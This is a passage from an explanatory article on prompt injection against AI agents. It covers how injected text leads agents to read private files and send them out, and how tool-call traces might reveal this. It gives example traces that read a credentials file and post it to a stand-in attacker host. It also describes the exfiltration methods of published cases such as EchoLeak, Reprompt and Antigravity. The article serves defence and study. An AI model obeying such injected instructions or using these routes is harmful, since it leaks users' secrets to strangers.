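# Prompt injection that makes an AI agent read files and send them out, and how its tool calls reveal it

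## How an agent turns text into actions on a computer

An AI agent is a large language model, a program trained to continue text, that runs in a loop in which it can call tools and read their results. The tools may be a file reader, a web browser, an email account or a command line. In a prompt injection attack, someone puts instructions where the agent will read them, such as in a web page or an email, and the agent carries them out although neither its user nor its operator (the organisation that runs it) intended that. If the agent can read private files and reach the network, the injected text can lead it to read a file and send the contents to a stranger. The attack uses tools that the operator gave the agent, so it requires no stolen password or broken software. The tool calls leave a record, and a defender who draws it as a graph, linking each call to the later calls that use its data,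 may be able to detect the file being sent out.

### The loop

A language model by itself only produces text. It takes in a sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words), outputs a likely next one, and repeats. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a documentation page for developers who build on the Claude models, explains that the model outputs a structured request and other software performs the operation, so the model never executes anything. The result then goes back into the conversation.

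Take a user who asks an agent to summarise a sales report on a shared drive. The application around the model first assembles the input: the system prompt (the operator's standing instructions), a description of each available tool, and the user's message. The tool descriptions are text as well. According to OpenAI's *Function calling*, the equivalent guide for that company's models, they go into the system message in a syntax familiar from training, and they use up part of the limited length of input that the model can take. The application joins all of this into one token sequence and the model continues it. Since the report is not in the sequence yet, a likely continuation is a tool call. In a shortened version of the format in Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, with an invented tool and file, it looks like this:

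```json
{"type": "tool_use", "id": "call_01", "name": "read_file",
 "input": {"path": "sales/q3.txt"}}
```

The application reads the name and the arguments, opens the file, and sends back:

```json
{"type": "tool_result", "tool_use_id": "call_01",
 "content": "Third-quarter sales rose 4 per cent ..."}
```

The identifier links the result to the request. The application appends both to the conversation and sends the whole sequence back to the model, which may respond with another call or with the summary. The loop ends when a response contains no tool call, because the model has produced its answer, hit a length limit, or refused.

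The application opens that file with the permissions of the account it runs under, so if that is the user's login, the call can access whatever the user can. The JSON doesn't record why the model produced the request. The result can contain any text. If someone had typed a sentence addressed to AI assistants into the sales report, that sentence would enter the sequence along with the sales figures. Anthropic's format puts the result in a message with the role "user", where the block type `tool_result` distinguishes it from the user's own words. One of OpenAI's interfaces gives tool results their own role, "tool".

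Liu, Ruan and colleagues (2025), in *TraceAegis*, a paper on spotting abnormal behaviour in agents, compress the loop into one line:

$$a_t = \pi(h_t, G, T)$$

Here $a_t$ is the action at step $t$, either a tool call or a special action that ends the task. The history $h_t = (a_1, o_1, \ldots, a_{t-1}, o_{t-1})$ lists each earlier action and its observation $o$, which for a tool call is the result. $G$ is the overall goal and $T$ is the set of available tools. The policy $\pi$, in practice the language model, maps $h_t$, $G$ and $T$ to the next action. In the sales example, $h_1$ is empty, $a_1$ is the call to `read_file`, $o_1$ is the text of the report, and $a_2$ finishes the task with a summary. For the summary to be useful, $a_2$ has to depend on $o_1$, and an attacker can exploit that dependence.

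### Function calling, the Model Context Protocol and gateways

The mechanism in the example is called function calling, or tool calling. A developer gives each function a name, a plain-language description and a schema, which formally defines the arguments it accepts. By default, the model's output determines which functions run and how often, and one response can contain several calls. OpenAI also offers a strict mode that guarantees the arguments fit the schema. This guarantees only the form of a call, so `path` will be a string but could name any file on the drive.

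With function calling alone, developers have to connect each application to each tool separately. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard that replaces these separate connections with a common format. TechTarget's *Stateless MCP seen as step forward for enterprise AI* reports that MCP originated at Anthropic and has belonged since 2025 to the Agentic AI Foundation, a subsidiary of the Linux Foundation. The Model Context Protocol (2025) specification distinguishes hosts (the applications that contain the language model), clients (connectors inside those applications) and servers (the services that offer data and tools). They exchange messages in JSON-RPC, an existing format for asking another program to run a procedure. The maintainers put downloads of their main software kits at close to half a billion a month in the July announcement of the current version, Model Context Protocol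 (2026).

The current Model Context Protocol (2026) specification describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model chooses which calls to make. It recommends but does not require that applications keep a human in the loop who can deny a call, and it prescribes no particular way of involving the user.

A gateway is software between the agent and its tools that can log, hold or block each call. It suits a detector because it needs no access to the model's internals. Liu and colleagues built their detector on gateway records because whoever monitors an agent often cannot obtain its prompts or reasoning. The records contain each tool's input and output and the order of the calls. The July version of MCP copies the tool's name into the header of the web request, so a gateway can route or authorise a call without opening the message body. The arguments stay in the body, so a gateway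 that reads only headers can detect that an agent used an email tool but misses the recipient and the text.

The same version removed the session identifier from the Model Context Protocol, and each request is now independent of the others. To group all the calls from one session, an operator has to add its own identifier. Some calls may never go through the operator's gateway. Anthropic runs certain tools, including web search and web fetching, on its own servers, and these calls have usually finished by the time the operator's application receives the response that lists them, so the operator can log them but can't block them.

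### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that gets a model to follow instructions that neither the operator nor the user intended. It is direct if the text arrives in the user's message and indirect if it arrives in content that a tool fetches. The name dates from 2022, when the programmer Simon Willison popularised it by analogy with SQL injection, an attack on databases. In 2023 Kai Greshake and colleagues described the indirect form in a preprint, with working attacks on several systems, including GPT-4. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter whose software uses a language model to score CVs. A candidate can attack it without access to the software, by hiding a line in the CV that tells the model to approve the application.

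In the notation above, indirect injection changes very little. Liu and colleagues write the step after a manipulated tool result as

$$a_{t+1} = \pi(h_t \oplus (a_t, o_t^*), G, T)$$

where $\oplus$ means "with this added at the end" and $o_t^*$ is the abnormal observation. The model, the goal and the tools are all as before. For trouble that comes in through the user's message they add that message, $u_t$, to the history instead. Their abnormal observations also include honest mistakes, such as a medical triage tool that sends a patient with a cough to psychiatry. An agent can thus go off course with no attacker present, which anyone who reads odd behaviour as proof of an attack should remember.

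The formula lists the goal $G$ and the history $h_t$ as separate inputs, but the model receives both as parts of the same token sequence. Databases had a similar weakness, which parameterised queries largely fixed. In these queries, the programmer sends the command and the values separately, so the database engine can never interpret a value as part of the command. David C argues that language models have nowhere to put such a barrier, because underneath they have no category of "data" or "instruction" and only predict the next token.

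Before text goes into a model, software inserts special control tokens to help the model tell the parts apart. These tokens mark where the system prompt, the user's message and the model's own replies begin. *Chat templates*, a guide from Hugging Face, the company that maintains a widely used library of models, notes that "The chat is still just a sequence of tokens". The guide shows two models, fine-tuned from the same base model, that use different markers. An earlier edition, *Templates for Chat Models*, adds that language models "do not intrinsically have special handling for roles". Any effect the markers have comes from training, which can fall short.

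*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) measures how far models fail to separate roles by their markers. The researchers wrapped identical passages of web text in the markers of each role and trained a simple classifier on the model's internal activations to tell the roles apart. Because the passages were the same, the classifier could only learn the effect of the markers. They then applied it to text written in the style of a user but marked as tool output. In one model, the classifier gave this text an 87.6 per cent probability of being a user's and 9.3 per cent of being a tool's, so the style outweighed the markers. Over 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2 per cent where the measured confusion was lowest to 70 per cent where it was highest.

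The markers do help somewhat. In a test with an agent that had command-line access and a file of secrets, Ye and colleagues found that ordinary injected commands worked in 26 per cent of attempts on one model and at most 2 per cent on each of the others. An attack designed to exploit the confusion worked in 56 to 70 per cent of attempts on every model. These were OpenAI models from 2025, and newer ones may do better or worse. David C calls it "very possible" that nobody will ever fully fix the problem, but neither source proves that a future model could not keep instructions and data apart. An operator running an agent today should assume that some injected text will get through.

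This is dangerous because the agent acts with the user's permissions. Security engineers have long known about the "confused deputy", a program with high privileges that someone with low privileges tricks into making a request for them. An agent that reads a stranger's web page can become one. The stranger cannot open the user's files, but the agent can, and if it follows instructions on the page to open them, it does so under the user's login. The computer's access control allows this because the user has permission to open those files. Engineers can fix the classical cases, but David C calls language models "inherently confusable" and so advises operators to limit what the agent can do, and to log its inputs, outputs and tool calls in enough detail to notice suspicious activity. He expects attackers to need several tries, so failed calls may reveal an attack early.

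### Terms for sessions and detectors

To judge a method that searches such logs, one needs names for what a session contains and for how often the method is right.

| Term | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Source | A tool call that brings private data into the agent's context | Reading a payroll spreadsheet |
| Sink | A tool call that carries data out of the operator's control | Sending an email to an outside address |
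| Trace | The recorded order of messages, tool calls, arguments and results in one session | The request for a summary, the `read_file` call with its path and result, the summary |
| Recall | The share of attacked sessions that a detector flags | 270 flagged out of 300 attacked: 90 per cent |
| Benign firing rate | The share of harmless sessions that a detector flags, also known as the false positive rate | 26 flagged out of 1,300 harmless: 2 per cent |
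| AUROC | The probability that a detector scores a random attacked session above a random harmless one; 0.5 is chance | Attacked sessions score 0.9 and 0.4, harmless ones 0.5 and 0.1; the attacked session scores higher in three of the four pairs, so 0.75 |

A tool's name does not always indicate whether a particular call is a source or a sink. For example, a command-line tool can read a file with one command and upload it with the next.

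The totals of 300 and 1,300 in the table come from the test sets that Liu and colleagues built, one for healthcare and one for corporate purchasing, with the same totals in each. The flagged counts are made up. The 300 abnormal cases include runs in which the calls merely came in the wrong order or did not fit together. Recall on these cases therefore measures how well a detector finds anomalies in general, and a detector with high recall could still miss a careful attacker.

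Recall should be read alongside the benign firing rate, because a detector that flags everything has perfect recall. Many detectors give each session a score, and the operator picks the threshold above which a score raises an alert. A lower threshold catches more attacks but usually flags more harmless sessions too. AUROC (the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve, which plots recall against the benign firing rate at every threshold) is useful for comparing detectors because it doesn't require choosing a threshold. The operator still has to choose one to use a detector, and two detectors with the same AUROC can differ a good deal in how many attacks they catch at a benign firing rate of, say, 1 per cent.

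## From an injected instruction to a file read and a network send

Suppose a software team's overnight build, which automatically turns source code into a working program, has failed. A developer asks an agent to read the build log and post a summary to the team's tracker, a web page that lists open problems. The developer also pastes in a troubleshooting note copied from a website. The agent has two tools: `read_file`, which returns the contents of a file, and `http_post`, which sends data to a web address. The agent makes two calls if the note is clean and four if it contains hidden instructions.

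```
Trace A (clean note)
1  read_file(logs/build.log)
2  http_post(tracker)

Trace B (note with hidden instructions)
1  read_file(logs/build.log)
2  read_file(config/credentials)
3  http_post(diagnostics.example)
4  http_post(tracker)
```

In Trace B, an attacker had added a paragraph to the web page before the developer copied it, perhaps in type too small or faint to notice. The attacker wrote, in effect, that nobody can diagnose this error without the project's access settings, and asked the reader to send them to a diagnostics service. The file `config/credentials` holds the passwords and keys the team's software uses to log in to other services, and the attacker controls `diagnostics.example`. The second call is a source and the third is a sink, and together they form a chain, which is a sequence of tool calls whose harm comes from their combination.

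### How Trace B unfolds

The developer's request and the pasted note reach the model in one message with one role marker, which labels the hidden paragraph as the user's own words. Even a model that separated roles perfectly could not tell the two apart by role. This makes the attack a direct injection, although the user is the victim. The hidden paragraph is also about the failed build, so a model trained to be helpful may treat it as part of the task.

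The model then picks a file to read. An attacker who knows the project can name one, but a vague description may be enough. Android Authority's *I hacked my own computer using OpenClaw and it was terrifyingly easy* (2026) describes a small test of this. The writer installed OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, on a spare computer with fake files and a throwaway email account, and had it summarise unread email every five minutes. He emailed the assistant from an unfamiliar address to ask for some bank details, without naming a file or a command. The agent listed the documents folder, picked a fake bank statement out of several files and emailed it back as an attachment.

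That agent ran on a small version of Qwen3, which can run on a home computer. GPT-4o mini would also send the bank details. GPT-5 Nano read the financial documents but asked for confirmation before sending anything, and two small Gemini models searched for the documents until the test hit a usage limit. All five models at least started the search, but one person's trial of cheap models can't show how often a current frontier model would comply.

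In Trace B, the application opens `config/credentials` and appends the contents to the conversation. The attacker doesn't have the credentials yet, but if an outside company hosts the model, that company has now received them, as Android Authority points out about its own test. The credentials also stay in the history $h_t$, so any later call can include them, whether it comes immediately or after twenty harmless calls.

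To call `http_post`, the model has to write an address and the data to send. It generates both token by token, so it can copy the credentials exactly, or summarise, translate or re-encode them. The address can also carry data, because whoever runs a web server can log every address requested from it. An agent can therefore send data out just by fetching a web page, even though the call looks like a read.

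The software around the model makes the request with its own network access, and the credentials arrive at the attacker's server. The agent then posts the build log summary to the tracker, so the developer sees the expected result and has little reason to look further. In the OpenClaw test, however, the agent sent off the bank statement instead of finishing its summary, which an attentive user might have noticed.

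### The chain as inserted calls

The formula from Liu and colleagues describes a single step of an agent that has gone off course. An, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *IPIGUARD*, a paper that proposes a defence for agents, describe the whole sequence instead. They write the calls that the user's task needs as

$$\mathcal{T}_u = \{t_u^1(a_u^1), \ldots, t_u^n(a_u^n)\}$$

where each $t$ is a tool and each $a$ is the set of arguments that the agent gives it. An injected instruction triggers a further sequence of calls, $\mathcal{T}_{adv}$, and the agent ends up carrying out a modified sequence $\mathcal{T}_{u'}$ that contains them:

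$$\mathcal{T}_u \to \mathcal{T}_{u'}, \qquad \mathcal{T}_{adv} \subseteq \mathcal{T}_{u'}$$

In the build example, $\mathcal{T}_u$ is Trace A and $\mathcal{T}_{u'}$ is Trace B. The injected part is

$$\mathcal{T}_{adv} = \{\texttt{read\_file(config/credentials)},\ \texttt{http\_post(diagnostics.example)}\}$$

and deleting it from Trace B gives Trace A back. An and colleagues define this for text that arrives in a tool's result, in which case the extra calls can only begin after that result. The pasted note is in the model's input from the start, so the agent could read the credentials before it has even opened the log. The formula also doesn't require the user's own calls to survive. In the OpenClaw test the injected calls displaced the rest of the task.

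Sometimes the attacker needs no extra calls at all. An and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to pay for an order while an injected instruction asks for a transfer to another account. The task already includes a transfer, so only the arguments have to change. The build example has a version of this too. Build logs sometimes contain access keys that a program has printed by mistake, and an attacker who wants the log itself only has to redirect the post:

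```
1  read_file(logs/build.log)
2  http_post(diagnostics.example)
```

The tools and their order are the same as in Trace A. An and colleagues consider attacks of this kind less feasible because an attacker usually doesn't know what the user will ask for. That is reasonable for a random web page, but someone who plants instructions in a note about failed builds can guess fairly well what its readers are doing.

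### Entry through the user's input

Trace B depends on a user who unknowingly passes on the attacker's text. When many people share an agent, the attacker can be one of the users. A customer service agent might have access to other customers' records, and a hostile user who gets it to look one up needs no network tool, because the agent's reply delivers the data. In a milder documented case, the delivery firm DPD switched off its customer service bot in January 2024 after customers discovered that it would swear if told to. The account, quoted in Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, a collection of blog posts named after three conditions for data theft, mentions no stolen data.

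Opening a link can also submit a question as if the user had typed it, because several chat services accept questions as part of a web address. *Reprompt*, published by the data security company Varonis in January 2026, describes an attack that used this feature against Copilot Personal, Microsoft's assistant for consumers. The victim had to click once on a genuine Microsoft link, and the attack continued after they closed the chat.

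The link led Copilot to fetch a page from the researchers' server with the user's name in the address. The server replied with an instruction to fetch another address containing the next piece of information, and so on. The researchers asked for the user's location, what Copilot had learned about the user, and a summary of the last conversation. They add that an attacker could have asked which files the user had opened that day. The attack began as direct injection and continued as indirect injection because the later instructions came in fetched pages, so a defender who read only the opening message could not have known what Copilot would send.

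Copilot's safeguard against leaking data in web addresses covered only the initial request, and Varonis advises vendors to apply such protections to repeated and follow-up requests too. TechRepublic's *How ‘Reprompt’ Attack Let Hackers Steal Data From Microsoft Copilot* (2026) reports that Microsoft patched the flaw in January. Varonis confirms the patch without saying what it changed, and mentions no victims. The flaw did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version for organisations, but in June 2026 Varonis announced a similar attack, SearchLeak, on Copilot's enterprise search. The same problem has also affected coding tools. The Hacker News lists a flaw, disclosed around the same time as Reprompt, in which malicious links to the code editor Cursor could lead to leaked access tokens.

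Injected instructions can also arrive in attached files. In September 2025, a day after the workspace application Notion released its AI agents, Abi Raghuram showed that white text on a white background in a PDF could make one of them leak a team's data. According to Willison, an agent asked to summarise the PDF would read the team's client list, combine the company names and revenue figures into one string, and put it into a web search that pointed to the attacker's server. Willison suggested that Notion stop its search tool from accepting web addresses. His post records neither Notion's response nor any real victims. Whether such a file counts as direct or indirect injection depends on the application, because some applications copy the file's text into the user's message while others have the agent open it with a tool.

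### Entry through content the agent fetches

Indirect injection requires nothing from the user beyond an ordinary request. EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, is an example. When an employee asks a question, Copilot first searches that person's mailbox, documents and chats, and adds what it finds to the model's input. Anyone who can send the employee an email can therefore get text into that input. Ravia (2025) explains in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* that once a question caused Copilot to retrieve the hostile email, the attacker could extract anything in the model's context, including the chat history, retrieved documents, and details that the application loads in advance, such as the names of the user and the organisation. Data loaded in advance enters the context without a tool call, so a log of calls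 may contain no record of its source.

Sending the data didn't require a tool call either. The injected instructions led the model to include an image in its answer, with the stolen data in the image's address. When the browser displayed the answer, it tried to load the image, and this request carried the data to the attacker's server through a Microsoft service on Copilot's list of approved addresses. The user saw at most a broken picture. An operator who records only tool calls would miss this transfer, so the log should also include any addresses in the agent's answers.

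Aim Labs, the research group that discovered EchoLeak, built a working attack in January 2025 and reported it privately to Microsoft. In their case study *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) date the fix to May and the public advisory to 11 June. Microsoft applied the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. The case study also mentions recent changes that make Copilot strip certain links and embedded images from incoming external content. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that the flaw had affected no customers, and Reddy and Gujral cite a statement that there was no evidence of real attacks.

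Reddy and Gujral's claim that EchoLeak is the first known case of a prompt injection causing concrete data theft in a production system is doubtful. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists more than a dozen earlier reports of the same kind of attack on widely used products, starting with ChatGPT in April 2023. Ravia makes the more careful claim that earlier attacks needed the user to direct the chatbot to a malicious page or could take only limited data, while EchoLeak had neither restriction. The victim still had to ask Copilot something, but almost any work question might be enough.

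Coding agents are an attractive target because the folders they work in often contain credentials. In November 2025 the security firm PromptArmor demonstrated an attack very similar to Trace B on Antigravity, Google's coding tool. A web page posing as an integration guide contained instructions in tiny type. As Willison recounts, the agent gathered code and cloud credentials from the project, wrote them into a web address and opened the address in its browser. By default, Antigravity's file tools can't open files that the developer has excluded from version control, which here included the credentials file, so the model read it from the command line instead. Google listed data theft through its browser agent as a known issue it was working to fix. If the developer had pasted the guide into the chat, the same text would have been a direct injection.

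PromptArmor repeated the attack in January 2026 on Claude Cowork, which Anthropic presented as a version of its coding agent, Claude Code, for work other than coding. The agent could read any files the user had made available. By default, it could contact only a short list of web domains, which included Anthropic's own service for developers. PromptArmor had the agent upload the files there, to the attacker's account. Willison mentions no fix or victims in his account of this demonstration.

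Vendors have mostly responded to such reports by blocking the routes by which data gets out. In July 2026, for example, Ayush Paul got Anthropic's Claude chat assistant to reveal a user's name, home city and employer through the links it chose to follow on a hostile website. Anthropic then stopped its web-fetching tool from following links found on pages it had fetched. The fix removes one way to exploit an injection, but injection is still possible because the tool can still read hostile text.

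Models may also have become harder to fool. Willison reports on an evaluation, commissioned by Anthropic, in which Trajectory Labs tried 72 indirect injection scenarios on the versions of Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex available in mid-July 2026. None of 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Code with three current Claude models in "auto mode", in which software rather than the user decides whether to allow each action. If the attempts were independent, this result would still be compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4 per cent (at 95 per cent confidence). They probably were not independent, because each scenario was tried ten times, and an attacker who studies the system may do better than a fixed test. Willison wants more independent confirmation, and doubts that auto mode could stop an agent from following the setup instructions of a software package that turns out to steal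 data.

### When the chain is possible

An operator can check whether an agent is vulnerable to this chain before any attack happens. According to Willison, an agent is vulnerable if it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally, which he calls the "lethal trifecta". If the agent has no access to private data, an attacker has none to steal. Without untrusted content, the attacker has no way to give the agent instructions, and without external communication, the agent cannot send the data out.

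The build agent has all three capabilities in both Trace A and Trace B. The trifecta is therefore a test of an agent's setup, and a detector that relied on it alone would flag every session of this agent, including the harmless ones. Willison worries most about users who assemble the combination by accident. The Model Context Protocol makes it easy to connect tools from different makers, none of whom can check what the others provide. Even a single connection can provide all three capabilities, as with GitHub's official server for the protocol, which could read public issue reports that anyone can write, read the user's private code, and publish proposed changes containing the private material.

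Meta turned the idea into a design rule. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) states that, until there is a reliable way to detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

- [A] it can process untrustworthy inputs;
- [B] it can access sensitive systems or private data;
- [C] it can change state or communicate externally.

Meta says an agent that needs all three without starting a fresh session should not run unsupervised, and asks for human approval or some other reliable check. The rule is broader than the trifecta because "change state" includes actions such as deleting files, which can do harm even if no data leaves.

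The team could bring the build agent into line with the rule in three ways. It could drop [A] by forbidding text from outside, but then the developer couldn't paste in the troubleshooting note. It could drop [B] by running the agent somewhere with no credentials and no secrets in its log. Or it could restrict [C], so that `http_post` works only for the tracker or a person approves each new destination. Willison thinks external communication is usually the easiest capability to remove. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, released in June 2026, takes this approach by limiting the network requests that ChatGPT can make, and doesn't try to keep injected text out. But restricting [C] works only if no approved destination will pass the data on to a stranger. In both EchoLeak and the Cowork demonstration, the data left through an approved address.

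Meta describes the attack as a path from [A] to [B] to [C], but the first two can also come in the opposite order. An agent might read credentials for a legitimate reason and open a hostile page ten calls later. The credentials are still in its context, so the page's author can ask for them. Meta's example of a safe configuration change avoids this problem. An agent may start by browsing the web without private data and then gain access to internal systems, provided that it permanently loses the ability to communicate at that point.

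Human approval is the weakest part of the rule. Meta itself warns that a user may confirm a warning without reading it. Willison describes an Anthropic study that measured how often this happens. The study had 1,053 paid developers work with a coding agent, and researchers replaced one permission request for each developer with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 per cent refused it. Anthropic calculated that auto mode would have blocked 89 per cent of the same actions, leaving about one in nine unblocked, though this result favours its own product. Both figures concern dangerous commands in general, and people might find it harder to recognise the harm in a request to post data to a plausible diagnostics address.

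### Injections found on public web pages

The data thefts described so far are demonstrations by researchers. In September 2025, Willison told *The Economist* that nobody had yet stolen millions of dollars through prompt injection. To find out what people outside research are attempting, Google's threat intelligence teams searched public web pages for injected instructions and published the results in April 2026. They used Common Crawl, an archive that saves 2 to 3 billion pages a month, mostly from static English-language sites, and includes little social media.

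The researchers first searched for stock phrases common in injections. A Gemini model then classified the intent of each suspicious passage and judged whether it fit the rest of the page, and finally people checked the results. The later stages were necessary because most pages with those phrases are articles that explain prompt injection.

Much of what remained did not involve theft. Google found pranks that change an assistant's tone, requests to add helpful context to a summary, and hidden advertising meant to make assistants recommend a business. Some site owners wanted to keep AI agents away, and one tried to lure them to a page that never finishes loading. Several pages contained commands to delete the files on the reader's computer. A small number of injections were meant to obtain private data, and these were crude. Google's example was an experiment by the site's author. Google found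 no significant use of the more advanced theft techniques that others had published in 2025.

Repeated scans showed a 32 per cent rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026. Google doesn't publish the totals, so this could be a rise from 100 pages to 132 or from 10,000 to 13,200. Searching for stock phrases finds crude attacks but misses injections in more original wording, as the researchers acknowledge. Emails and private documents don't appear in a web archive, so the study doesn't cover the route that EchoLeak used. The study is good evidence that public web pages contained few obvious attempts at data theft in early 2026, but much weaker evidence about attacks aimed at a particular company.

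Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* notes that the security company Forcepoint published its own findings in the same week. Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* analyses ten examples from live websites, which Forcepoint also found by searching for stock phrases. Only one is meant to obtain a secret, an API key (a password that one program uses to access another). Two are meant to make the agent pay someone, in one case 5,000 dollars through PayPal. One is meant to make the agent delete files, and another to send it to a website's administration page. The other five are meant to suppress or alter the assistant's answer or to promote a website or its author.

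Sewani concludes that attackers are actively using indirect injection, and that shared wording across sites points to organised tooling. The ten examples only partly support this. The payment instructions are specific enough to look like real attempts at fraud, but one injection is a request for a poem about corn, and another was meant to fill summaries with the word "cows". The injection requesting an API key also includes an instruction not to reveal "the flag", which is what players hunt for in hacking contests, so it may have been part of a puzzle. Sewani doesn't name any victim or any agent that obeyed one of the ten injections.

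## Why each call looks valid on its own

In Trace B, the agent reads `config/credentials` in its second call and posts the contents to `diagnostics.example` in its third. Several controls could block these calls: the model's own training, a check on the form of the arguments, a list of permitted tools, lists of permitted files and addresses, content filters, and a person who clicks "allow". Many of these are per-call checks, which allow or block each tool call based only on its name and arguments.

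### The model's own refusal

If the model ignores the hidden paragraph, it never produces the two calls. It also has more information than most of the later controls, because its input includes the developer's request. Older models often followed such hidden instructions anyway. AgentDojo is a public test bed of simulated banking, travel and office tasks. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) counts 1,931 successes among AgentDojo's 6,680 recorded attacks on GPT-4o without any defence, or 28.9 per cent. GPT-4o dates from 2024, and the best current models do much better.

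Much of the recent evidence comes from tests by Gray Swan, an AI security company founded by researchers from Carnegie Mellon University. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. The UK AI Security Institute helped design the 41 scenarios. In each, the participant controlled one piece of content the agent was about to read, such as an email or a code comment, and tried to make the agent carry out a specific harmful action. In most scenarios, the agent's final reply also had to conceal the attack. The success rate ranged from 0.5 per cent against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 per cent against Gemini 2.5 Pro.

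Participants could read the conversation so far and knew exactly which call they wanted, advantages an outside attacker usually lacks. Dziemian and colleagues therefore treat their results as an upper bound for attacks that get a single turn. But if an agent leaked data and then mentioned it in its reply, the attempt usually counted as a failure, even though the data would already have been gone. The harmful actions also had to fit the agent's job, such as an email-sorting agent marking a message about a contract deadline as read. A successful attack of this kind produces a call that the agent could plausibly have made anyway, which is harder for every later control to catch.

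Gray Swan, government institutes in the UK and the US, and several developers then built a benchmark with 28 new scenarios and 1,130 attacks, chosen because they worked on several models. Anthropic published results for it in July 2026 in the system card (the test report released with a new model) for Claude Opus 5. In December, Gray Swan released newer figures in its *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, a public record of safety tests. The December rows below come from two news reports on the tracker, iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* and Fakti.bg's *Some AI Models Lie to Achieve Higher Scores*.

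| Model | Date of results | Success in one attempt (per cent) | Success within 15 attempts (per cent) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | July 2026 | 0.2 | 2.0 |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | July 2026 | not given | 16.5 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | July 2026 | 3.1 | 20.0 |
| Gemini 4 Argon (Google) | December 2026 | not given | 2.3 |
| Gemini 4 Carbon (Google) | December 2026 | not given | 2.5 |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro (Moonshot) | December 2026 | not given | 64.7 |
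| Nemotron 3.5 Super VL (Nvidia) | December 2026 | not given | 94.3 |

The tracker refers to version 2.0 of the benchmark, so the July and December rows may not be comparable. iAfrica reports that Anthropic's newer models came close behind Google's. The July figures are Anthropic's account of its own product and its rivals'. However, Anthropic tested its own models without extra safeguards and the others through their public services, which may include some. Gray Swan (2026) states that it pays for its public tests and controls what it publishes. It also does private evaluations for AI developers.

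If each attempt on GPT-5.6 Sol had the same independent 3.1 per cent chance of success, at least one of 15 attempts would succeed about 38 per cent of the time. The measured figure is 20 per cent, which suggests that the successes cluster in some scenarios. An operator whose agent resembles one of those scenarios faces a higher risk than the average implies.

Anthropic's tests with an adaptive attacker show the clustering. Shade, an automated tool from Gray Swan, made 200 attempts in each of 40 coding scenarios. Against Opus 5 with extended thinking on, 0.56 per cent of attempts succeeded, or about 45 out of 8,000, and those successes fell in 13 of the 40 scenarios. The rate per attempt matters to an attacker who can send an agent only one email, but the number of vulnerable scenarios matters to one who can keep sending them. Resistance in one setting also doesn't reliably predict resistance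 in another. Against Claude Mythos 5, 0.45 per cent of attempts succeeded in the coding test and 29.7 per cent in a separate browser test. VentureBeat reported a similar gap for an earlier model, Claude Opus 4.6, which resisted all 200 attempts in a coding environment but failed to resist 17.8 per cent of single attempts when it operated a graphical interface.

According to Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, OpenAI reported in October that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99 per cent of direct prompt injections and 97.13 per cent of indirect ones. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) describes a similar gap in the previous generation. These scores are hard to compare with Gray Swan's without the number of attempts per scenario. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) also reports that the company's latest models have saturated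 the commonly used tests, so high scores on them have become less informative. It presents an automated attacker that OpenAI trained to find new weaknesses.

A large collection of attacks can give false confidence if most of them are the same attack. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes an experiment in which university researchers retrained a small model, Qwen3-4B, on successful attacks found by two automated tools. They then tried new attacks on 40 tasks already known to be vulnerable. The version trained on 7,132 attacks failed on up to 19 tasks, compared with up to 11 for the version trained on 4,282. The researchers suspect that the tools had mostly reworded a few tricks. The test is small, but the larger collection produced the weaker defence in three of the four set-ups.

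Gray Swan's benchmark places its attacks in content that the agent reads while it works. In Trace B, the hostile paragraph is in the user's message, so the published rates for indirect injection don't directly apply. Suppose the model complies and produces the call to read the credentials.

### Form and permission

Schema validation checks only the form of the arguments, so both calls pass. CrowdStrike's *How Agentic Tool Chain Attacks Threaten AI Agent Security* (2026), a post by a security vendor, advises developers to define the allowed values of every argument, not just its type and format. The schema then contains an allowlist, a list of the only values the operator accepts.

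The tool permissions also allow both calls. The developer asked the agent to read a log and post a summary, so it needs `read_file` and `http_post`. Kekatos and colleagues mention rules that restrict an agent to the tools for its current task. Such a rule would have helped if the developer had wanted the summary in the chat, because the operator could then have withheld `http_post`. But here the theft uses the same two tools as the legitimate task. The operating system also allows the read, because the developer's account may open the file.

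### Permitted paths and destinations

A path allowlist could stop the theft at the second call by confining `read_file` to the `logs` folder, so that the credentials file never enters the context. An agent that only summarises logs could still do its job, but one that also repairs builds may need the configuration folder, and the operator would then have to permit the read. The restriction also has to cover every other tool that can open a file, including the command line that the agent used in the Antigravity demonstration.

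A destination allowlist that contains only the tracker stops the third call, even if the credentials are already in the context. The allowlist must apply to every field that can hold an address. In an example from CrowdStrike, the email tool is sound, but hidden text in another tool's description gets the agent to blind-copy an outsider. The user asked for the email and its main recipient is correct, so a check on that recipient alone would pass it.

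### Content filters

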